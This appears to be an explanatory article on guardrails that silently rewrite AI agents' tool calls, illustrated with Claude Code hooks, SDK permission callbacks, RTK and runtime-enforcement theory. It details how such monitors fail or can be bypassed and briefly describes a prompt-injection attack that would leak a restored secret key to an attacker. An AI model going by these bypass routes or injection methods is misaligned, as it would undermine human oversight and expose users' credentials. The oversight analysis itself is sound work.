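# Silent Rewriting of AI Agents' Tool Calls by Guardrails

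## What is tool-input rewriting?

Tool-input rewriting means changing an AI agent's action after the model writes it and before any software carries it out. An agent here is a language model that works in a loop, proposing tool calls and reading their results. A tool call is a structured request to run a named tool, such as a shell or a file editor, and its arguments (the text of a shell command, say) are the tool input. Software around the model can alter that input before it reaches the tool. It might point a file write at a different directory, remove a password, or add a flag that makes the command a dry run, in which the program only reports what it would have done. Some products don't notify the model of the change, which makes the rewrite silent.

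Operators have ordinary security reasons for wanting this power. *Agentao* (Jin, 2026) lists excessive privileges, uncontrolled side effects and prompt injection, an attack that plants instructions in material the agent reads, among the risks of tool-using agents. An agent may issue hundreds of commands, which makes it impractical for a person to read each one first, so operators use a program to check them. Most such programs only allow or block a command, but a program that rewrites substitutes an action of its own.

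### The agent loop

A language model cannot run anything by itself. It produces text, and the harness, the software around the model, turns some of that text into action. Anthropic's *How the agent loop works*, part of the developer documentation for the company's Claude models, describes the cycle. With the guardrail check written out as a step of its own, it runs like this:

1. The harness sends the model the user's request, together with standing instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the history so far.
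2. The model replies with text, with one or more tool calls, or with both.
3. The harness checks each proposed call against whatever rules the operator has set.
4. If the check lets the call through, the tool runs.
5. The harness adds the result to the transcript, the stored sequence of messages, tool calls and results, and the model continues from there. The loop ends when the model replies without a tool call.

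OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, works the same way. InfoQ's *OpenAI Begins Article Series on Codex CLI Internals* (2026) describes Codex's harness as a loop that takes the user's input and uses a model to generate tool calls or replies.

In Anthropic's worked example, a user asks the model to fix the failing tests in auth.ts. The model calls the shell to run the test suite, and three tests fail. It reads the source file and the test file, edits the source, and runs the suite again. All three tests pass, and the model tells the user so.

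The model based that closing sentence entirely on the transcript, which is its only record of the session. It read the test result in the text that the harness placed after its call. OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* explains that the prompt from which the model continues grows as the conversation grows. If something between steps 2 and 4 had narrowed the test command to a single file and skipped the failing tests, the result would have come back clean, and the model could have written the same sentence.

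The guardrail layer performs the check at step 3. It consists of the hooks, permission callbacks and gateways that inspect or change calls outside the model. A hook is code that the operator supplies and the harness runs at a fixed point, such as just before a tool executes. A permission callback passes the call to the application, which may ask a person to review it. A gateway is a separate service through which calls pass. Jin builds Agentao around the split between what the model proposes and what the host authorises, but disclaims any formal safety guarantee for it.

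*A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) distinguishes the moment when the model generates a tool call's arguments from the moment when the call crosses the system boundary and takes effect. Input rewriting has to happen between the two, while a guardrail can still stop or alter the call locally. After the crossing, the guardrail can only try to compensate, and some effects, such as a sent email, can't be undone.

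### What a guardrail can do with a proposed call

Anthropic's *Hooks reference* for Claude Code, its coding agent, lists four decisions that a hook can return before a tool runs. The hook can also change the tool's input. These outcomes differ in whether the tool runs and in who learns why.

| Outcome | Does the tool run? | Who receives the reason |
| :- | :- | :- |
| Allow | Yes, unless a separate rule forbids it or demands confirmation | Nobody in the session; it goes to a debug log |
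| Deny | No | The model |
| Ask | Only if a person confirms | The person, in the permission prompt |
| Defer | Not yet; the turn ends and another program can resume the call later | Nobody in the session; it goes to a debug log |
| Rewrite | Yes, with changed input, if the accompanying decision permits | A rewrite carries no reason of its own; the operator may attach a note for the model |

Deferral is for applications that have no terminal where they can ask the user a question. The application pauses the agent at the call, collects an answer through its own interface and restarts the session, and the call then goes through the same check again. When several hooks disagree, denial takes priority, followed by deferral, asking the user, and allowing the call. A hook that returns nothing does not approve the call, which then goes through the normal permission rules.

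A rewrite changes the content of a tool call but is not a verdict on it, so an operator pairs the rewrite with a verdict. The changed call runs without a prompt if the verdict is "allow", but a person sees it first if the verdict is "ask". Claude Code ignores a rewrite that comes with a deferral.

Tallam argues that agents in production need more than a yes or no from a guardrail, because blocking every doubtful action makes an agent useless and allowing every one makes it dangerous. The paper proposes six interventions: pause, escalate to a higher authority, narrow the agent's permissions, modify, defer, and roll back. Tool-input rewriting is the "modify" intervention, in which a function maps the proposed action *a* to another action *a′*, and the system hands *a′* back to the agent as though the agent had written it. In Tallam's example, the model puts a sensitive raw identifier into a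 call, and the guardrail replaces it with a token.

Under that definition, the agent's later reasoning works from *a′*, so the model has a correct record of what ran but does not know that anything changed. If a harness runs *a′* but leaves *a* in the transcript, the model still does not know about the change, and its record is also wrong. Tallam's "modify" is more a specification than a finding, because the paper measures the core of a policy engine and leaves a trial with live agents to later work.

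Some guardrails have the agent correct its own action instead of rewriting it. In *OSGuard* (2026), a safety benchmark for agents that operate a computer's interface, the guardrail holds back an action that it judges unsafe or unrelated to the task and returns a short explanation, and the agent proposes a revised action from the same state. The guardrail in *GuardianAgentBench* (2026) can pass a call, block it, or return corrective feedback. If the agent uses up its retries without fixing the problem, the guardrail permanently blocks the call and sends a person an alert with the full history. Under both designs, only actions the model wrote can run. Correction takes extra rounds of the loop, though, and retries are limited because the agent may never fix the problem. A rewrite takes only one step because the guardrail corrects the action without the model.

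### The same call, denied and rewritten

An agent might propose the shell command `rm -rf /tmp/build` to delete an old build directory. The command prints nothing when it succeeds.

If the guardrail denies the call, a rejection message appears in the transcript in place of a result, and the model can read there that nothing ran. According to Anthropic, Claude typically then tries a different approach or reports that it could not proceed.

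A guardrail can instead rewrite the call. A sample callback in Anthropic's *Handle approvals and user input* confines shell commands to a sandbox by replacing `/tmp` with `/tmp/sandbox`, so `rm -rf /tmp/build` becomes `rm -rf /tmp/sandbox/build`. If that directory doesn't exist, the command still succeeds because the `-f` option suppresses the error. The result is empty and free of errors, just as it would be if `/tmp/build` had been deleted, but the old build is still on the disk.

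Some rewrites leave more of a trace. A sample hook in Anthropic's *Intercept and control agent behavior with hooks* adds `/sandbox` to the start of the path whenever the agent writes a file, and the tool's result names the changed path instead of the one Claude requested. A model that compared the two could work out that something had happened, but only because this tool happens to print its path, and many shell commands print nothing similar.

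### Proposed, executed and reported action

In the deletion example, the proposed action is the tool call as the model wrote it (delete `/tmp/build`). The executed action is the call as it ran (delete `/tmp/sandbox/build`). The reported action is the agent's later account, perhaps "I removed the old build". This account matches the proposed action but misdescribes the executed one. It would be odd to call it a lie, since the agent's transcript supports it, and a reviewer who compared the two would find nothing wrong.

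Tool-input rewriting makes false reports harder to interpret. When every call runs as written, an agent that gives a false account of what it did has either made a mistake or deceived someone. When a guardrail can rewrite calls, the agent may instead have accurately reported the call it wrote, unaware that a different one ran. A reader needs to see the executed action to rule this explanation in or out.

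In its engineering guidance on evaluating agents, Anthropic makes a similar distinction between the transcript and the outcome. An agent may finish by telling the customer that it has booked a flight, but the outcome is whether a reservation exists in the database. Checking the outcome is good practice and would show that the agent's report of deleting the build was false. It would not show why, because bookings and deletions can fail for many reasons that don't involve a rewrite.

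### Who may be unaware

The difference between the proposed and the executed action matters to four parties. The model plans its next step based on what it assumes happened. The user relies on the result. The approver, who may be a person or a program, permits the call. The auditor later reconstructs events. A lone developer may be the user, approver and auditor, while a large company may split these roles among three departments, and information held by one may not reach the others.

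A rewrite is silent if the model gets no notice of it, even if the application openly showed the change to the person who approved the call. For example, Anthropic's guide to approvals describes how application developers can let a person approve a call with changes. The application alters the input, and Claude sees the result but "isn't told you changed anything".

Like the model, the user may not know that a call was rewritten. Administrators can install Claude Code hooks across an organisation, and developers, who may never have read the hooks' code, cannot switch them off in their own settings. If such a hook rewrites a call and allows it, the developer normally sees no permission prompt, and the hook's stated reason goes to the debug log.

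Rewriting can also mislead the approver, because the command that was approved may not be the one that runs. In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier reviews calls in place of a person, and it reviews the input that Claude wrote. If a hook changes the input afterwards, the approval no longer matches the command. Claude Code can deny the changed call to prevent a command the approver hasn't seen from running. In some sessions the denial message mentions that a hook changed the input, so the model learns of the rewrite as a by-product.

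A transcript that preserves the model's original call shows the action the model proposed, while an operating system's process log shows the action that was executed. Each record looks complete on its own, so an auditor can only discover that a guardrail changed the call by comparing the two.

### Changes that are not input rewriting

Operators can also alter other text in an agent session, with different effects. A hook on the user's prompt can block the prompt or add context, which may influence the model's decision, but the model still chooses its own action. A hook that runs after a tool can replace the tool's output before the model reads it. Anthropic warns that this changes only what Claude sees, because any file operations, commands and network requests have already taken effect. A hook on the display can change the agent's words on the user's screen, for example to hide an API key,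 while the transcript keeps the original. Tallam's "modify" is broader than input rewriting because it covers plans, retrieval queries and tool responses as well as arguments.

The harness itself also adjusts some inputs. If a requested timeout is too long, Claude Code lowers it to the permitted maximum instead of rejecting the call. The executed action then differs from the proposed one, though few people would call this a guardrail.

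These mechanisms can be combined. The path in the sandboxed file write's result revealed the rewrite, but an operator who also replaced that result could remove the clue. Anthropic cautions that even without a rewrite, removing error details from a tool's output can lead Claude to proceed on a false assumption.

Of the ways a guardrail can intervene, input rewriting is the one that changes what happens in the world and can still leave the model with a record of a different action. It stops the dangerous command from running and lets the agent keep working, without spending a round of the loop arguing with it. But because the model isn't told about the change, the transcript contains a wrong record, and the transcript is where the model looks first and where its overseers often do too. When does silently changing an action make an agent safer, and what problems does it create for the people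 who must oversee the agent?

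## How does a rewrite happen in current agent software?

Anthropic documents input rewriting in Claude Code in enough detail to trace a call from the model's proposal to the result the model reads. Suppose an operator wants to keep agents from publishing code on their own without interrupting their tasks. The operator writes a hook that turns every `git push`, the command that uploads changes to a shared code repository, into a dry run.

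### One call through Claude Code

The model has fixed a login bug and proposes `git push origin main`. In Anthropic's agent loop, hooks run only after the model has finished its message, so the model has already written the original command when the hook starts.

Just before the tool runs, the harness triggers an event named `PreToolUse` and looks for hooks that the operator has registered for that tool. It sends each one a description of the call in JSON, a text format for structured data. Without session details such as the working directory, the push hook receives this:

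```json
{
  "hook_event_name": "PreToolUse",
  "tool_name": "Bash",
  "tool_input": {
    "command": "git push origin main",
    "description": "Publish the login fix",
    "timeout": 120000
  },
  "tool_use_id": "toolu_01ABC"
}
```

`Bash` is the shell tool, and `tool_input` holds what the model wrote: the command, a short description of it and a time limit in milliseconds. The hook runs the operator's code and prints a reply:

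```json
{
  "hookSpecificOutput": {
    "hookEventName": "PreToolUse",
    "permissionDecision": "allow",
    "permissionDecisionReason": "Agents may only rehearse a push",
    "updatedInput": {
      "command": "git push --dry-run origin main",
      "description": "Publish the login fix",
      "timeout": 120000
    }
  }
}
```

The `updatedInput` field contains the rewrite. Claude Code replaces the whole input with this object, so the hook has to copy the description and the time limit even though it only adds `--dry-run`. The copied description still reads "Publish the login fix", although the new command publishes nothing.

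Claude Code then checks the changed command against the operator's permission rules, according to Anthropic's hooks reference. A rule against all pushes would stop the dry run too, and a hook can't get a forbidden command past the rules by substituting it for a permitted one. But a rewrite can change a call that the rules would have refused into one they allow, for example by moving a file write from a protected directory to a permitted one.

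The shell runs `git push --dry-run origin main` if no rule forbids it. Git contacts the shared repository, works out what it would upload and prints a summary without uploading anything. The summary has the same form as the one for a real push, with a line that ends in `main -> main`. The harness returns this output under `toolu_01ABC`, the identifier of the model's original call, so it looks like the result of an ordinary push.

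The hook's reason, "Agents may only rehearse a push", goes to the debug log, where the model can't read it. The operator could have added a note for the model in another field, `additionalContext`, but this hook leaves it out.

The feature is hard to date exactly. According to SkillsMP, a third-party directory of add-ons for coding agents, Claude Code 2.1.0 fixed hooks so that they could return changed input together with an "ask" decision. Before the fix, a hook could not both change a command and ask a person to confirm it. The fix implies that rewriting itself is older than version 2.1.0.

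### What a hook can change

Almost every Claude Code tool accepts a rewritten input. A hook can change the path, the text to find and the replacement text in a file edit, or the query and the list of permitted sites in a web search. It can also change the instructions that an agent gives to a subagent, a second agent that handles part of the task. The subagent then follows the changed instructions, and the first agent may read its report as a response to the original ones.

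The harness sometimes changes the input before any hook receives it. For file tools, Claude Code turns relative paths into absolute ones, so that a different spelling of the same path doesn't get around a hook's check. When the model presents a plan for approval, it has already saved the plan to a file and typically sends an empty input, to which Claude Code adds the plan's text. A log of what a hook receives therefore doesn't always contain the model's exact words.

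Claude Code also uses `updatedInput` for a purpose unrelated to guardrails. When the model sends the user a multiple-choice question, it leaves the answers blank. An application that collects the answers through its own interface can have a hook return them in `updatedInput`. The mechanism is the same as in the push example, but here the model left the content blank for someone else to fill in.

### "Approve with changes"

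Developers can use Anthropic's Agent SDK to build their own applications around Claude. When a tool call needs approval, the SDK's permission callback, `canUseTool`, returns "allow" or "deny", and an "allow" can include a changed input.

Anthropic lists this option as "approve with changes" and recommends it for sanitising parameters, adding constraints and limiting access. Anthropic told developers in the May 2026 edition of its guide that Claude doesn't learn of the change, and repeated this in the Chinese edition in July 2026. It still offers the option.

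The same guide also describes ways to refuse a tool call and inform the model. In one example, the agent tries to delete files, and the callback blocks the command with a message that the user would like Claude to compress the files into an archive instead. A developer could get the same archive by silently replacing the delete command with a compression command, but then the model would have no reason to think that the user wanted to keep the files.

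The harness skips the callback if a permission rule or the session's permission mode has already allowed the call. File path restrictions that exist only in the callback therefore don't apply to those calls, and Anthropic recommends checking them with a `PreToolUse` hook.

Claude Code also has a `PermissionRequest` hook, which runs when the harness is about to ask a person for permission. The hook can allow the call with a changed input, which Claude Code then checks against its "deny" and "ask" rules. If the application also has a permission callback, the two run at the same time and the first decision counts. So if the callback allows the original input before the hook decides, the rewrite never takes effect.

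### How other products compare

GitHub provides a similar hook in its Copilot SDK, a toolkit for building applications on its coding assistant. The hook receives the tool's name and arguments and can return `modifiedArgs`, a changed set of arguments. GitHub's example adds a 30-second time limit to any shell command that lacks one. An agent's long test run could then stop early because of a limit the agent had not set.

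When Copilot's hook denies a call, the user sees the reason, while Claude Code shows it to the model. Copilot's hook can also set `suppressOutput`, which keeps the tool's output out of the conversation, and GitHub warns that the model won't see it. A single reply from the hook can therefore change a command and hide its output. Claude Code accepts a field with the same name but ignores it, so an operator who wants to change the output needs a separate hook that runs after the tool.

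Both products let the developer who writes a hook attach a note for the model. GitHub doesn't describe any automatic notice to the model when a hook changes arguments, so a developer who wants the model to know about a rewrite has to write the note.

Other tools let different parties rewrite calls. LangChain, a library for building agents, lets a human reviewer edit a proposed call. Developers have also proposed interceptors that can change messages in the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to outside tools. An interceptor could run in a gateway, which would receive the model's original call from the harness and forward a different one.

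The harness keeps the transcript, so a gateway outside the harness can't correct the call stored there. If the gateway's operator wants the model to know that the call was changed, the gateway can include a notice in the result it returns.

| Mechanism | What it can change | What the model reads next |
| :- | :- | :- |
| Claude Code, `PreToolUse` hook | The whole input of a call | The tool's result, plus a note if the operator wrote one |
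| Claude Code, `PermissionRequest` hook | The whole input, if the hook also allows the call | The tool's result |
| Claude Agent SDK, permission callback | The input of a call that still needs approval | The tool's result, without any mention of the change |
| GitHub Copilot SDK, pre-tool hook | The arguments of a call | The tool's result, unless the hook hides it, plus a note if the developer wrote one |
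| Gateway outside the harness | Calls and results that pass through it | Whatever result the gateway returns |
| Tallam's "modify" (a proposed design) | Plans, retrieval queries, arguments and responses | The changed version in place of the original |

### What the transcript contains afterwards

After a guardrail rewrites a call, the harness can keep the original call in the record the model sees, replace it with the changed call, or add a notice of the change.

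**The harness can keep the original call in the transcript.** In the push example, the transcript then contains `git push origin main`, followed by the output of a dry run. This design is the easiest to build because the model has finished its message before the hook runs, so the harness only has to leave that message unchanged.

A guardrail can **replace the call** in the transcript. The transcript then contains `git push --dry-run origin main`, as if the model had written the `--dry-run` flag itself. Tallam's "modify" intervention works this way.

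Replacement has an advantage when the guardrail's change has to last. If the transcript kept the raw identifier from Tallam's example, the model might copy it into the next call, and the guardrail would have to replace it with a token again.

But replacing one call doesn't make the rest of the transcript consistent with it. If the model wrote "I'll publish the fix now" just before the push, that sentence stays next to a command that publishes nothing. The model may also have copied the sensitive identifier from an earlier tool result, which still contains it. Tallam's architecture can reduce this second problem because it also lets a guardrail rewrite a tool's response before the agent continues.

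Tallam lists seven points in an agent's work where a guardrail might act, from forming a plan to writing the audit record. According to the paper, rewriting plans and arguments is straightforward in systems with separate components for planning and execution. Rewriting a retrieval query or a tool's response needs its own hook. The harness must also let the guardrail substitute the action. Claude Code's `updatedInput` field requires less, because it only has to change what the tool receives.

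**Adding a notice.** The harness can keep the original call and put a message beside the result, such as "This command ran with --dry-run". The transcript then shows the model's proposal, the change and the outcome. Claude Code and the Copilot SDK support this through `additionalContext`. Claude Code also saves the message with the session, so the model can still read it if someone resumes the session. If a hook's author fills in only the changed input, the rewrite is silent, because the notice goes in a separate field.

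### How rewrites fail

The most serious failure for an operator is that the original command runs without being rewritten. By default, if a hook script is missing or stops before it prints a valid reply, Claude Code shows the user an error notice and continues with the call. In the push example, the agent's real push would go ahead unless a permission rule stopped it. The transcript would then be accurate, because the model's own command had run.

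A hook that takes too long has the same effect. Claude Code cancels most hooks after ten minutes unless the operator sets another limit. It then discards any output and sends the original call through the normal permission rules. However, if a hook that a developer wrote as a function inside an Agent SDK application times out before a tool call, Claude Code blocks the call.

Since version 2.1.295, operators can set `onFailure` to "block" so that a hook's crash or timeout stops the call. The setting works for hooks that run a command or contact a web address, except those that Claude Code runs in the background. By default, if a hook prints a valid rewrite but exits with code 1, which usually signals an error, Claude Code still applies the rewrite. With `onFailure` set to "block", it treats that exit as a failure and stops the call.

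Even this setting misses one kind of failure. Claude Code reads a hook's reply as JSON only if a single JSON object is the hook's entire output. Some computers print a greeting or status line whenever a shell starts, and if that line comes before the object, Claude Code treats the whole output as plain text. The harness records plain text from a command hook as a success, ignores the rewrite and continues with the original call. The operator sees no error and may believe that the guardrail works.

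Two working hooks can also undo each other's changes. Suppose one hook adds `--dry-run` to pushes and another removes passwords from commands. Claude Code runs matching hooks in parallel, and each reply replaces the entire input. If a push contains a password, the harness therefore uses either a dry run that still contains the password or a real push without it.

Claude Code ranks conflicting verdicts, with denial first, but this ranking doesn't combine two rewrites that both come with "allow". At least one open-source coding agent keeps the rewrite from whichever hook comes last in the configuration file. This makes the outcome predictable but still discards a change. An operator can avoid the conflict by making both changes in a single hook.

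Sometimes the harness runs a hook but ignores its rewrite. Claude Code's Monitor tool also starts shell commands, and in recent versions a hook registered only for the Bash tool runs on them too. The hook can deny such a command or have Claude Code ask the user, but its `updatedInput` has no effect. To rewrite these commands, the operator has to register the hook for Monitor by name or for all tools. In auto mode, Claude Code can also discard a rewrite when the model repeats a changed call that Claude Code had denied. Cursor, an AI code editor, has dropped changes that a hook made to a file's content, which is a problem for an operator who relies on the hook to keep passwords out of files.

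Other faults damage the call instead of leaving it unchanged. `updatedInput` replaces all of the call's arguments, so a hook that returns only a new path for a file write drops the text to be written. GitHub warns developers to keep changed arguments in the form the tool expects, and its example copies the existing arguments before adding the time limit. An early bug in Anthropic's Python SDK replaced a call's arguments with an empty object.

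Before version 2.1.207, Claude Code denied a call with a validation error if the permission callback returned "allow" without an input. It now runs the model's original input. This is more convenient for a developer who wants to approve the call unchanged, but a developer who meant to return a changed input and forgot to include it no longer gets an error.

A hook can also miss commands and file reads it was meant to rewrite. On Windows, Claude Code may send commands through a PowerShell tool, which a hook registered only for Bash doesn't cover. Windows paths also use backslashes, so a hook that looks for `/src/` finds no match in `C:\project\src\index.ts` and leaves the call unchanged. When a user mentions a file with the `@` sign, Claude Code by default inserts the file's contents into the prompt without a tool call, so a hook that redirects file reads has nothing to rewrite.

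## What gets rewritten, and does the intended effect survive?

A hook can catch the right command and still replace it with one that does the wrong thing. Computer scientists had a test for such replacements long before coding agents existed, because operating systems and web browsers also run programs that the computer's owner doesn't fully trust. Software called a monitor sits between such a program and the machine, checks the actions the program attempts, and may change them.

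### A test from runtime-enforcement theory

*Edit Automata* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2003) models a monitor as a machine that reads the sequence of actions a program requests and outputs the sequence that runs. Earlier theory dealt with monitors that could only halt the program just before it broke a rule. The paper adds monitors that can suppress an action while the program continues, and monitors that can insert actions. An edit automaton can do both, so it can replace an action by suppressing it and inserting a different one. A hook that changes `git push` to `git push --dry-run` makes this kind of replacement.

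A monitor in this theory has to meet two requirements. Soundness means that everything the monitor lets through obeys the policy, whatever the program asked for. Transparency means that if the program's actions already obey the policy, the monitor preserves their meaning. Write σ for the requested sequence, σ′ for the sequence that runs, and P for the policy. For every σ, then:

1. P(σ′) holds.
2. If P(σ) holds, then σ ≅ σ′.

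The sign ≅ means that two sequences have the same effect, and the monitor's designer has to define what counts as the same. For example, closing a file twice may be equivalent to closing it once, and the order in which a program opens two files may not matter. Soundness is easy to achieve without transparency, since a monitor that blocks everything never breaks a rule, but such a monitor is useless.

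A monitor is transparent in this sense if it has no noticeable effect on a well-behaved program. It doesn't have to disclose its rewrites, so a rewrite can be both transparent and silent.

Ligatti and colleagues also define a stricter standard, precise enforcement, under which the monitor must let each permitted action through before it considers the next. They recommend it for interactive programs that, like agents, need the result of one action before they can continue. If the program can attempt any sequence of actions, a monitor that can insert or suppress actions can precisely enforce the same policies as one that can only halt the program. For agents, this means that rewriting can keep the agent working, but it doesn't let an operator enforce any rule that stopping the agent couldn't.

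Neither requirement determines what should replace a forbidden action. Transparency covers only permitted behaviour, and any replacement the policy allows satisfies soundness. In *Do you really mean what you actually enforced?*, Bielova and Massacci (2008) re-examined an example by Ligatti and his co-authors and found that the same violation can be handled very differently. In the example, customers at a market must pay for the apples they take. Suppose a customer takes one apple, browses without paying, then pays for two apples and takes two. Bielova and Massacci expected a monitor to replace the theft with a warning and let the rest through. The automaton in the original example issued the warning and completed the sale, but dropped the browsing. An automaton built by the method in the original proof output nothing.

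Edit automata also leave out the results of actions. A program that reads input and prints it back falls outside the model, because its second action depends on what the first one returned. Ligatti and Reddy (2010), in *A Theory of Runtime Enforcement, with Results*, filled this gap with mandatory results automata, monitors that can change both an action and the result the program receives. In one of their examples, a program lists a directory with `ls`. The system returns `foo.txt` and `.hidden`, and the monitor passes on only `foo.txt`. In another, a program tries to shut the computer down, and the monitor first shows the user a confirmation box.

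This model suits agents better because the monitor must return a result before the program takes its next step. It has no separate transparency requirement. Ligatti and Reddy explain that a policy can refer to the program's original request, so the designer can specify in the policy which changes the monitor may make and what the program must receive afterwards. An operator could use such a policy to require a notice for every changed command, or to forbid such notices.

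Soundness is harder to achieve in a coding agent than in the theory. Ligatti and colleagues warn that a monitor can't enforce a policy on actions it can't observe. A hook receives the text of a shell command, such as `make release`, but the `git push` may be inside a script the command runs. Anthropic calls the filter that decides which shell commands trigger a hook "best-effort" and tells operators to use the permission system for firm prohibitions. An operator who must prevent publication would do better to withhold the publishing credentials as well.

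### Forced dry runs

Operators force dry runs of commands that are hard to undo, such as those that publish code or change live servers. A dry run is as safe as blocking the command, and it also reports some of the errors that the real command would hit. The agent can fix those errors before a person runs the real command.

```text
before:  kubectl apply -f web.yaml
after:   kubectl apply --dry-run=server -f web.yaml

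before:  terraform apply -auto-approve
after:   terraform plan

before:  npm publish
after:   npm publish --dry-run
```

All three tools simulate only part of the real operation. `kubectl` sends requests to Kubernetes, a system that runs software across many machines. With `--dry-run=server`, the server checks the request as usual but doesn't store it. This catches a misspelled field or a missing permission, but not a misspelled software image name, because Kubernetes tries to download the image only after storing the request.

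Terraform creates cloud resources from configuration files. Its `apply` command has no dry-run flag, so a hook has to replace it with `plan` and remove `-auto-approve`, which `plan` rejects. `terraform plan` compares the configuration with the existing resources and lists the changes it would make. It marks some values as known only after the real run, when the cloud provider assigns them. The provider can still refuse a change that looked fine in the plan, for instance if the account has reached a quota.

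npm publishes JavaScript packages to a public registry. `npm publish --dry-run` lists the files that would go into the package and uploads nothing. If the user isn't logged in, the dry run only prints a warning, whereas the real command stops with an error. Some npm commands ignore the flag altogether. According to npm's documentation, one of them is `dist-tag`, which can change the version that people get by default when they install a package. A hook that added `--dry-run` to every npm command would let that change go through.

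Short flags carry a similar risk. With `git push`, `-n` means a dry run, but with `git commit` it skips some of the project's own checks. A hook that added `-n` to both commands would make pushes safer but commits less safe.

A carefully written hook can avoid these mistakes by adding the right flag only to commands that honour it. Suppose agents may not publish packages. A hook that adds the flag to every `npm publish` and leaves all other commands alone is sound, because nothing reaches the registry, and transparent, because every permitted command runs as written. It passes the theoretical test even though it defeats the agent's purpose every time the agent tries to publish.

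Cancelling publication can also disrupt later steps. If the agent's next command tries to install the new version from the registry, it fails because the version isn't there, and the model may wrongly treat the package as published. The dry run preserves the intended effect only if the original command was meant only to preview publication, for example to see which files the package would contain.

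### Secret redaction

Agents sometimes write passwords and access keys directly into commands, from which they can spread to shell histories and logs. A guardrail can remove the key before the command runs, but the result depends on what it puts in the key's place:

```bash
# Proposed by the model
curl -H "Authorization: Bearer sk-test-8d41" https://api.example.com/orders

# Key deleted
curl -H "Authorization: Bearer " https://api.example.com/orders

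# Key replaced with an environment variable
curl -H "Authorization: Bearer $ORDERS_KEY" https://api.example.com/orders
```

`curl` sends a request to a web address, and the service uses the key to identify the caller. When the guardrail deletes the key, the service rejects the request and the agent gets an authentication error for a command that looks correct in its transcript. The agent may then treat the key as expired. Storing the key in an environment variable avoids this problem. The shell looks up the value of `ORDERS_KEY` before it starts `curl`, so the service receives the request the model wrote.

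A guardrail that replaces a key with a variable is harder to build than one that deletes the key, because deletion only requires recognising the key, while replacement also requires a copy of that key stored under a known name. Ligatti and colleagues list keys and passwords among the data that a monitor may be unable to produce itself, in which case it can't insert actions that need them.

Whether the substitution works also depends on how the shell handles the variable. If the model had put the header in single quotes, the service would receive the literal text `$ORDERS_KEY`, and the call would fail. If the variable were unset, the service would receive an empty value, as if the guardrail had deleted the key. Even when the substitution works, the real key appears in the arguments of the running `curl` process, where other monitoring software on the machine may record it.

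Changing the command also comes too late to keep the key from the model, which has already written it. To do that, the guardrail has to put a placeholder in the text the model reads and swap it back when a command needs the real key:

1. The agent opens a settings file that contains the key `sk-test-8d41`.
2. The guardrail replaces the key in the result with `{{SECRET_1}}` and remembers the pair.
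3. The model writes a `curl` command with `{{SECRET_1}}` in the header.
4. The guardrail puts the real key back just before the command runs, and the service accepts the request.
5. If the service's reply repeats the key, the guardrail replaces it with `{{SECRET_1}}` again before the model reads it.

The guardrail here acts as a mandatory results automaton because it changes both the actions and their results. The executed command differs from the proposed one but still has the intended effect, because the model used the placeholder to stand for the key.

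The guardrail still needs a rule for when to restore the key. If it restored keys in every command, an attacker who planted instructions in a web page could have the agent send `{{SECRET_1}}` to the attacker's server, and the guardrail would fill in the real key. Restoring a key only in requests to the service it belongs to prevents this. But with this rule, if the agent copies the placeholder into a settings file, the file contains the literal text `{{SECRET_1}}`, and any program that reads it will fail to log in.

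Encoding causes a different leak. Many services expect a password in base64, a standard way of writing data as plain characters. If the agent runs a command that encodes the restored key and prints it, the output no longer matches the guardrail's pattern, so the model receives the key in a form that anyone can decode.

### Commands wrapped to shorten their output

Some operators rewrite commands to save money. Providers charge for model use by the token, a word or fragment of a word, and long command outputs fill the transcript with tokens that the model processes again at every step. RTK (short for Rust Token Killer) is an open-source program that runs a command and condenses its output before the agent reads it. Its Claude Code hook puts the program's name in front of supported commands:

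```text
before:  git status
after:   rtk git status
```

According to the project's README, "Claude never sees the rewrite". But the default installation adds an instruction file about RTK, so the model may know that the tool exists without knowing which of its commands go through it. RTK groups similar items, collapses repeated lines and cuts material it classifies as noise. It reduces 15 lines of output from a successful `git push` to `ok main`, and more than 200 lines from a failing test run to about 20 lines on the failures. When a command fails, RTK also saves the full output to a file that the model can open.

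RTK has to meet a stricter requirement than the dry-run hook. No policy forbids `git status`, so transparency applies to every command that RTK rewrites. For a command that only reads information, preserving the meaning also means preserving whatever the output's reader needs, and that reader may be another program.

Users have reported several cases where RTK failed this test. RTK's *bug(rewrite): hook rewrites left-hand side of piped commands, breaking downstream filters* (2026) describes a search for running Python processes:

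```text
before:  ps aux | grep python | grep -v grep
after:   rtk ps aux | grep python | grep -v grep
```

The `|` sign passes the output of one command to the next. `ps aux` lists every running process, and the `grep` commands pick out the lines that mention Python. Because RTK had reformatted the list, `grep` found no matches even when Python was running.

Programs also signal whether they succeeded through a number called an exit code. RTK's *fix(git): propagate exit codes in push/pull/fetch/stash/worktree* (2026) repaired a fault in which a failed `git push` printed an error but returned the code for success. A script containing `git push || handle_error` would therefore not have run its error handler when the push failed. RTK merged the fix in March 2026, but a later list of related faults in its issue tracker includes an open report that the tool prints "ok" for pushes GitHub has rejected.

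Besides losing information, rewriting can corrupt the output or confuse the model. One RTK user found duplicated lines and stray markup in the text returned to the agent, although the commands had changed the files on disk correctly. In another report to RTK (2026), a user ran the tool with OpenCode, an open-source coding agent, which displayed the rewritten command in the session. The model had asked for `ruff`, a program that checks Python code, but saw `rtk ruff` instead. It reasoned, "I keep accidentally typing 'rtk' instead of 'ruff'", and ran the check again to be safe. The hook rewrote the command again, and the model repeated the check several times even though each run found no problems.

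Independent developer LK4D4 built *rtk-codex-hook*, which comes close to applying the transparency test directly. It rewrites a command for OpenAI's Codex only when the RTK version is a safe equivalent. It leaves unchanged any command that would change something or that it can't interpret with certainty. This gives up some savings to avoid breaking as many commands.

RTK's README estimates that wrapping commands cuts their output in a 30-minute session from 118,000 tokens to about 23,900, a reduction of 80%. The project's website gives a lower figure, an average of 56% on the commands that RTK rewrites. Both figures cover only command output, which is part of what a session costs.

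JetBrains, which makes software for programmers, measured RTK's effect on total cost in *Does “rtk” skill really cut agent tokens by 60–90%?* (2026). It ran Claude Code on 86 automatically graded tasks with and without RTK, at low and high reasoning effort. At low effort, RTK raised the median cost per task by 7.6%, and sessions took 13.8% more turns. At high effort, it made no measurable difference to cost. Task quality stayed the same at both levels. At low effort, scores rose on 5 tasks, fell on 4 and tied on 71.

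JetBrains had analyzed 83 older transcripts and predicted that RTK would have a small effect. Claude Code reads and searches files mostly with built-in tools that a shell hook doesn't cover, and RTK doesn't support many shell commands. The commands it could rewrite produced just under 20% of all tool output. Even if RTK cut that output by 70%, the agent would use only about 3% fewer input tokens, because tool output is a fraction of what the model processes.

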